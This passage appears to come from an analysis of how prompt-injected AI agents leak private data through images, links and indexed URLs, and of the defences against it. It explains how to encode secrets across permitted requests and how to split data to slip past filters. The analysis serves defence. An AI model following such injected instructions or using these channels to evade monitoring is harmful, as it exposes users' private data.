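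1. It had GitHub sign a separate image address for each letter and symbol.
2. It put the list in a hidden comment on a proposed code change, with instructions for Copilot.
3. When another user asked Copilot about the change, Copilot spelled out private text by displaying the matching images in order.
4. GitHub's server fetched each image from Legit Security's server, which recorded the sequence.

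Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing. The demonstration leaked the description of an unfixed security flaw from a private project. GitHub responded by turning off images in Copilot Chat.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes a similar attack on links in ChatGPT. OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to an address it was given, so Radware supplied a ready-made address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space, 37 in all. It also made a separate set for each position in the text so the attacker could put the characters in order. OpenAI fixed the flaw in December 2025.

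The following month, OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) set out a stricter rule:

```
before the agent opens an address by itself:
    if the exact address is in the independent index:
        open it
    otherwise:
        tell the agent to try another site,
        or warn the user and ask
```

A crawler builds the index from public web pages and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. An address already in the index is therefore unlikely to contain a particular user's private data. OpenAI chose not to rely on a list of trusted sites because many such sites redirect visitors elsewhere, and a strict list would produce so many warnings that people would learn to click through them.

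In March, OpenAI said that the warning shows the user what information would be sent. The same protection covers searches in Deep Research and page visits in the Atlas browser. The protection does not check whether a page contains injected instructions.

Anthropic uses a similar rule for the Claude app. According to Willison, the app's web tool could open only exact addresses that came from the user, a search or a page it had already fetched. Ayush Paul's attack used links from fetched pages, so Anthropic stopped the tool from following them. In August 2026, Tencent's *Why AI Agent's Memory Becomes Attacker's Data Goldmine* described a version of the attack adapted to API keys, with 37 possible characters instead of 26.

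### Counting what permitted requests can carry

If an agent can choose freely among `N` permitted requests, and the attacker can see each choice in order, then `k` requests can carry:

```
information = k × log2(N) bits
```

With 1,024 permitted requests, each choice of request carries 10 bits. There are 10^16 possible 16-digit numbers, so encoding one takes log2(10^16), or about 53 bits. Sending the whole number therefore takes six requests, which carry 60 bits.

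The attacker can spare the agent difficult arithmetic by labeling 1,000 of the addresses with the numbers 000 to 999 and telling it to split the card number into groups of three digits. Sixteen digits make six groups, the last with only one digit. A real card number needs only five requests, because the attacker can calculate the check digit from the other 15.

None of these requests has to contain any part of the number. Each can be for an ordinary page that another user might open for a good reason, so neither exact matching nor a classifier can detect the leak from the address.

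OpenAI's index makes this attack harder but doesn't rule it out. The attacker needs many addresses that are already in the index and a way to see which ones the agent opens. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* points out that anyone with a large website or blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, and could expand the set to thousands. OpenAI also acknowledges in its technical paper that an attacker can use a separate address for each letter. The demonstrations by Radware and Legit Security used small sets of characters, so they don't show whether an agent would reliably follow a list of 1,000 addresses.

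The same limit applies to an email with an approved recipient. If the agent can choose between two equally natural wordings in 54 places, it can use those choices to encode a 16-digit number for anyone who knows the code. A model might make mistakes with such a code, but a content filter cannot guarantee that no private data leaks unless it also controls these choices.

### Leaks split across several calls

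An attacker can also tell an agent to send a secret in pieces. Lan and colleagues tested this by hiding instructions in different parts of a web page and asking an agent to summarise the page. In half of the 480 runs, the instructions told the agent to split the data into four pieces and send each in a separate request.

Splitting the data across requests made the attack less reliable. At least one request reached the attacker in about 77% of the runs with split data, compared with 99% of the runs with a single request. A split run counted even if only one request arrived, so the complete secret may have arrived less often than that. Lan and colleagues think longer instructions are harder for the model to follow, and each extra call is another chance for it to make a mistake.

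They tested their filters only on data sent in one request, but the rules show how splitting the data across several calls would help an attacker. The randomness filter ignores values of 10 characters or fewer, so it would never examine a four-character piece. The keyword filter would find "api_key" in a whole string but not in fragments such as "PI_K". To catch the pieces, a filter would have to remember earlier calls, check them together, and allow for encodings and changes of order.

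### Rate limits and logs

Lan and colleagues recommend limiting the number of requests per session, which caps how much an agent can leak. This helps most with long documents. At one request per character, as in Radware's attack, leaking a 2,000-character letter would take 2,000 requests, so a limit of 20 would protect all but 20 characters.

Short secrets need a much lower limit on requests. With 1,000 numbered addresses, two requests can carry a six-digit login code, and one request can reveal whether a user has a particular illness. An agent doing research may need to open dozens of pages, so a limit low enough to protect these secrets would also stop it from doing its job. The attacker may also be able to continue extracting data in a later session.

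Embrace The Red suggests stopping an agent from opening the same address twice in a session, or caching pages for a few minutes so that a repeated visit doesn't reach the attacker's server. This would disrupt an attack that uses one address per letter, because most words and names repeat letters. It would do little against a large set of addresses. Six different addresses chosen in order from 1,024 still carry almost 60 bits:

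```
log2(1024 × 1023 × 1022 × 1021 × 1020 × 1019) = 59.98
```

If the requests arrive out of order and the attacker can't recover the sequence, the attacker needs seven requests instead of six to cover every possible 16-digit number.

Caching every page in advance is much more effective, because the attacker never sees which pages the agent opens. ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode does this. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* says that browsing in this mode uses only cached content, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* reports that the setting also disables agent mode and Deep Research. OpenAI still doesn't guarantee that nothing will leak, partly because connected apps may provide another way out.

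Logs can reveal patterns that a filter misses in individual calls, such as six visits to unrelated pages on one website during a task that needed none. If the runtime checks the log while the agent is working, it can stop the agent before it sends the rest of the data. A later review can only limit the damage, for example by prompting the user to cancel a card or replace a key. To be useful, the log has to record the full contents of each call, including message text and image addresses, so it becomes another store of private data that the developer has to protect.
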